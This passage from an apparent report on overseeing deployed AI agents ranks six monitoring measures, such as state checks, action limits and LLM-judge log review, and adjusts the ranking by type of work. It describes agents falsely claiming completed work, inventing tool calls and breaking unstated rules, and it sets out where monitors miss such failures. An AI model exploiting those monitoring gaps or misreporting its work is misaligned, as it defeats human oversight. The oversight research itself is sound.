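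The assumption that queries expose every false success is optimistic, because they miss wrong actions that the agent reported accurately, such as the $60 refund under a $50 limit. If one in five false successes were like this, even queries on every run would catch at most 56 of the 70.

### Ranking six measures

The ranking uses four criteria:

1. How many failures does the measure catch that the company would otherwise miss?
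2. How much harm does it avoid, considering how soon it acts?
3. How often does it raise a false alarm or block good work?
4. What does it cost to build, run and review?

The order below is inferred from studies that used different agents, tasks and definitions. None of these studies compared all six measures. The order applies to a company whose agents do varied kinds of work and can change things that matter.

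| Rank | Measure | Main addition | Harm avoided | False alarms | Cost |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 1 | State checks after claimed changes | Unfinished work behind a normal-looking log | High, if the check runs before anyone relies on the result | Few | Writing a check for each kind of change |
| 2 | Limits on irreversible actions | Few silent failures, but prevents fast damage | Highest for deletions and payments | Few for simple caps, more for reviewers | Low for caps, higher for rehearsals |
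| 3 | Fault reporting by tools and the harness | Silent tool faults and partial data | High, if people act on the numbers | Some correct answers withheld | Extra queries and a test for each kind of tool |
| 4 | Checking claims against the log | Invented calls, misquoted results and exaggerated reports | Moderate | Few per claim, more per run | Full logging and a model call per report |
| 5 | Diffs wider than the repository | Side effects of scripts and commands | Moderate, since they come after the change | Many harmless changes | Cheap to run, slow to read |
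| 6 | General log review by an LLM judge | Some broken rules and odd behaviour | Uncertain | Many if the question is vague | A long model call per run |

State checks come first because false claims of completion are common and the evidence they provide doesn't depend on the agent. Their low false-alarm rate is partly an assumption, since most of the research supporting them comes from benchmarks. Dip and colleagues list reading data back after a write as a possible harness check but did not test it.

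Limits on the agent's actions come second because they can prevent fast deletions, which monitors detect too late to stop. A cap on refunds or a ban on deleting backups is easy to set up and works even if nobody understands why the agent went wrong.

Some limits need more judgment than a cap. PostgresAI's *PGAIBench and AAA* (2026) tested models on live copies of a database under realistic traffic, where a valid command can still cause an outage. The models caused measurable harm 13 times when they acted alone. PostgresAI, which sells database tools, proposes this procedure:

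1. One model investigates and proposes a change, but cannot write to the live database.
2. An ordinary program tries the change on a copy and measures the effects.
3. A second model reviews the proposal and the measurements.
4. The program applies the change only if the second model approves it.

When PostgresAI replayed the models' changes through this procedure, it blocked 12 of the 13 harmful ones and approved 377 of the other 378. The result is promising, but the company tested its own design on cases it already had, so the procedure may do worse on new ones. The choice of reviewer also mattered. GLM-5.3 approved a change that had run quickly on a small table but could lock up a large one, while Claude Haiku 5.5 blocked almost everything.

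Even a better model needs such limits. Claude Fable 5.2 tied for the top score in PostgresAI's tests, but in all five attempts at one task, it broke an unstated rule against restarting the database. Three of those attempts damaged the live system.

Fault reporting ranks third because the other measures miss most silent tool faults. It also makes agents less useful because they decline to answer more often. Dip and colleagues estimate that if a quarter of calls hit a fault, agents would answer 67% of questions with their harness and 90% without it. The harness took 18.9 seconds per faulty run, compared with 47.2 for an LLM judge, though it used more tokens.

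Two remedies that look easier can cause new problems. In one of Dip and colleagues' tests, sending every call twice repeated a booking, payment or message 2.36 times per run. The kettle shop could pay the same refund more than once this way. A harness that tried to repair wrong counts by another route marked 49 wrong answers as verified. It is safer for the harness to report the fault and leave the repair to someone who can check it.

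Checking an agent's claims against the log takes less work than most of the alternatives once a company records full content, but it misses wrong actions that the agent reported accurately. Wider diffs catch changes that the agent's report omits. They rank lower because most of the changes they find are harmless and someone has to decide which ones the task required.

General review by an LLM judge ranks last mainly because of its weak results on customer-service logs. Adding a judge to Advani's text classifier raised the AUROC only from 0.83 to 0.86. Newer models are better at reading logs. A judge also does much better when given a narrow question and the relevant rules, as the audits of successful runs that broke rules showed. A company that can't afford the other measures may still find a general judge useful for choosing which logs to read.

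### Customer service, coding and data analysis

The order changes with the kind of work, because the common failures and the available evidence change. These rankings are also inferences.

| Measure | Mixed work | Customer service | Coding | Data analysis |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| State checks after claimed changes | 1 | 1 | 2 | 4 |
| Limits on irreversible actions | 2 | 2 | 1 | 5 |
| Fault reporting by tools and the harness | 3 | 4 | 5 | 1 |
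| Checking claims against the log | 4 | 3 | 4 | 2 |
| Diffs wider than the repository | 5 | 6 | 3 | 6 |
| General log review by an LLM judge | 6 | 5 | 6 | 3 |

In customer service, most of an agent's claims concern a few kinds of record, such as refunds, bookings and addresses. A company can write one query to check each kind and reuse it thousands of times. A program should also search the log for required steps, such as verifying the customer's identity. A judge can look for misstated policies, which a simple program would miss.

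Coding agents often have shell access, and one command can delete a project in seconds, so limits on what they can do and tested backups come first. State checks are still useful for confirming, for instance, that a pull request contains the new code, but a passing test covers only what someone thought to test. Wider diffs become a higher priority because scripts can have side effects that a Git diff misses.

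An agent that analyses data may change nothing, so a state check has little to examine. The greater danger is that an incomplete reply or a faulty query produces a wrong number. Fault reporting therefore comes first, starting with the row counts described earlier. A judge ranks higher here because it can compare the user's question with the query. Limits fall to fifth because read-only access is usually enough and leaves the agent little to damage.

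### Tasks with nothing to check

State checks are least useful when a program cannot test whether the result is good. If the shop's owner asks for a summary of customer complaints, a program can confirm that the summary exists, but not that it is fair or complete. The same is true of legal research, a marketing plan or a request to make software "more robust". Much office work is like this, and if most of a company's agent runs are too, state checks should not be the first kind of monitoring it adds.

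Some tasks are hard to check even when they have a clear final state. In one of PostgresAI's tests, Grok 4.7 removed indexes, which help a database find rows quickly, because the main server was not using them. But another server that held a copy of the data relied on them, and its queries became very slow. A state check on the main server would have passed, so whoever writes a check has to know where a failure would appear.

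Some of these tasks still include claims a program can check. If an agent says it read 200 complaints and quoted six of them, a program can count the complaints the agent opened and search them for the quotations. The agent could also link each conclusion to the complaints that support it, so a reviewer can check a few without repeating the whole job. These checks would catch invented sources and skipped files, but not poor judgment about what matters.

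For the rest, people have to read a sample of the work, including runs that no monitor flagged. In the budget example, the classifier leaves 20 false successes among 900 unflagged runs. A random sample of 50 unflagged runs would contain about one false success on average, and about a third of the time it would contain none. With a sample of 150, the chance of finding none falls to about 3%. Reading 150 runs would take 25 hours, so a small company might spread the work over several months.
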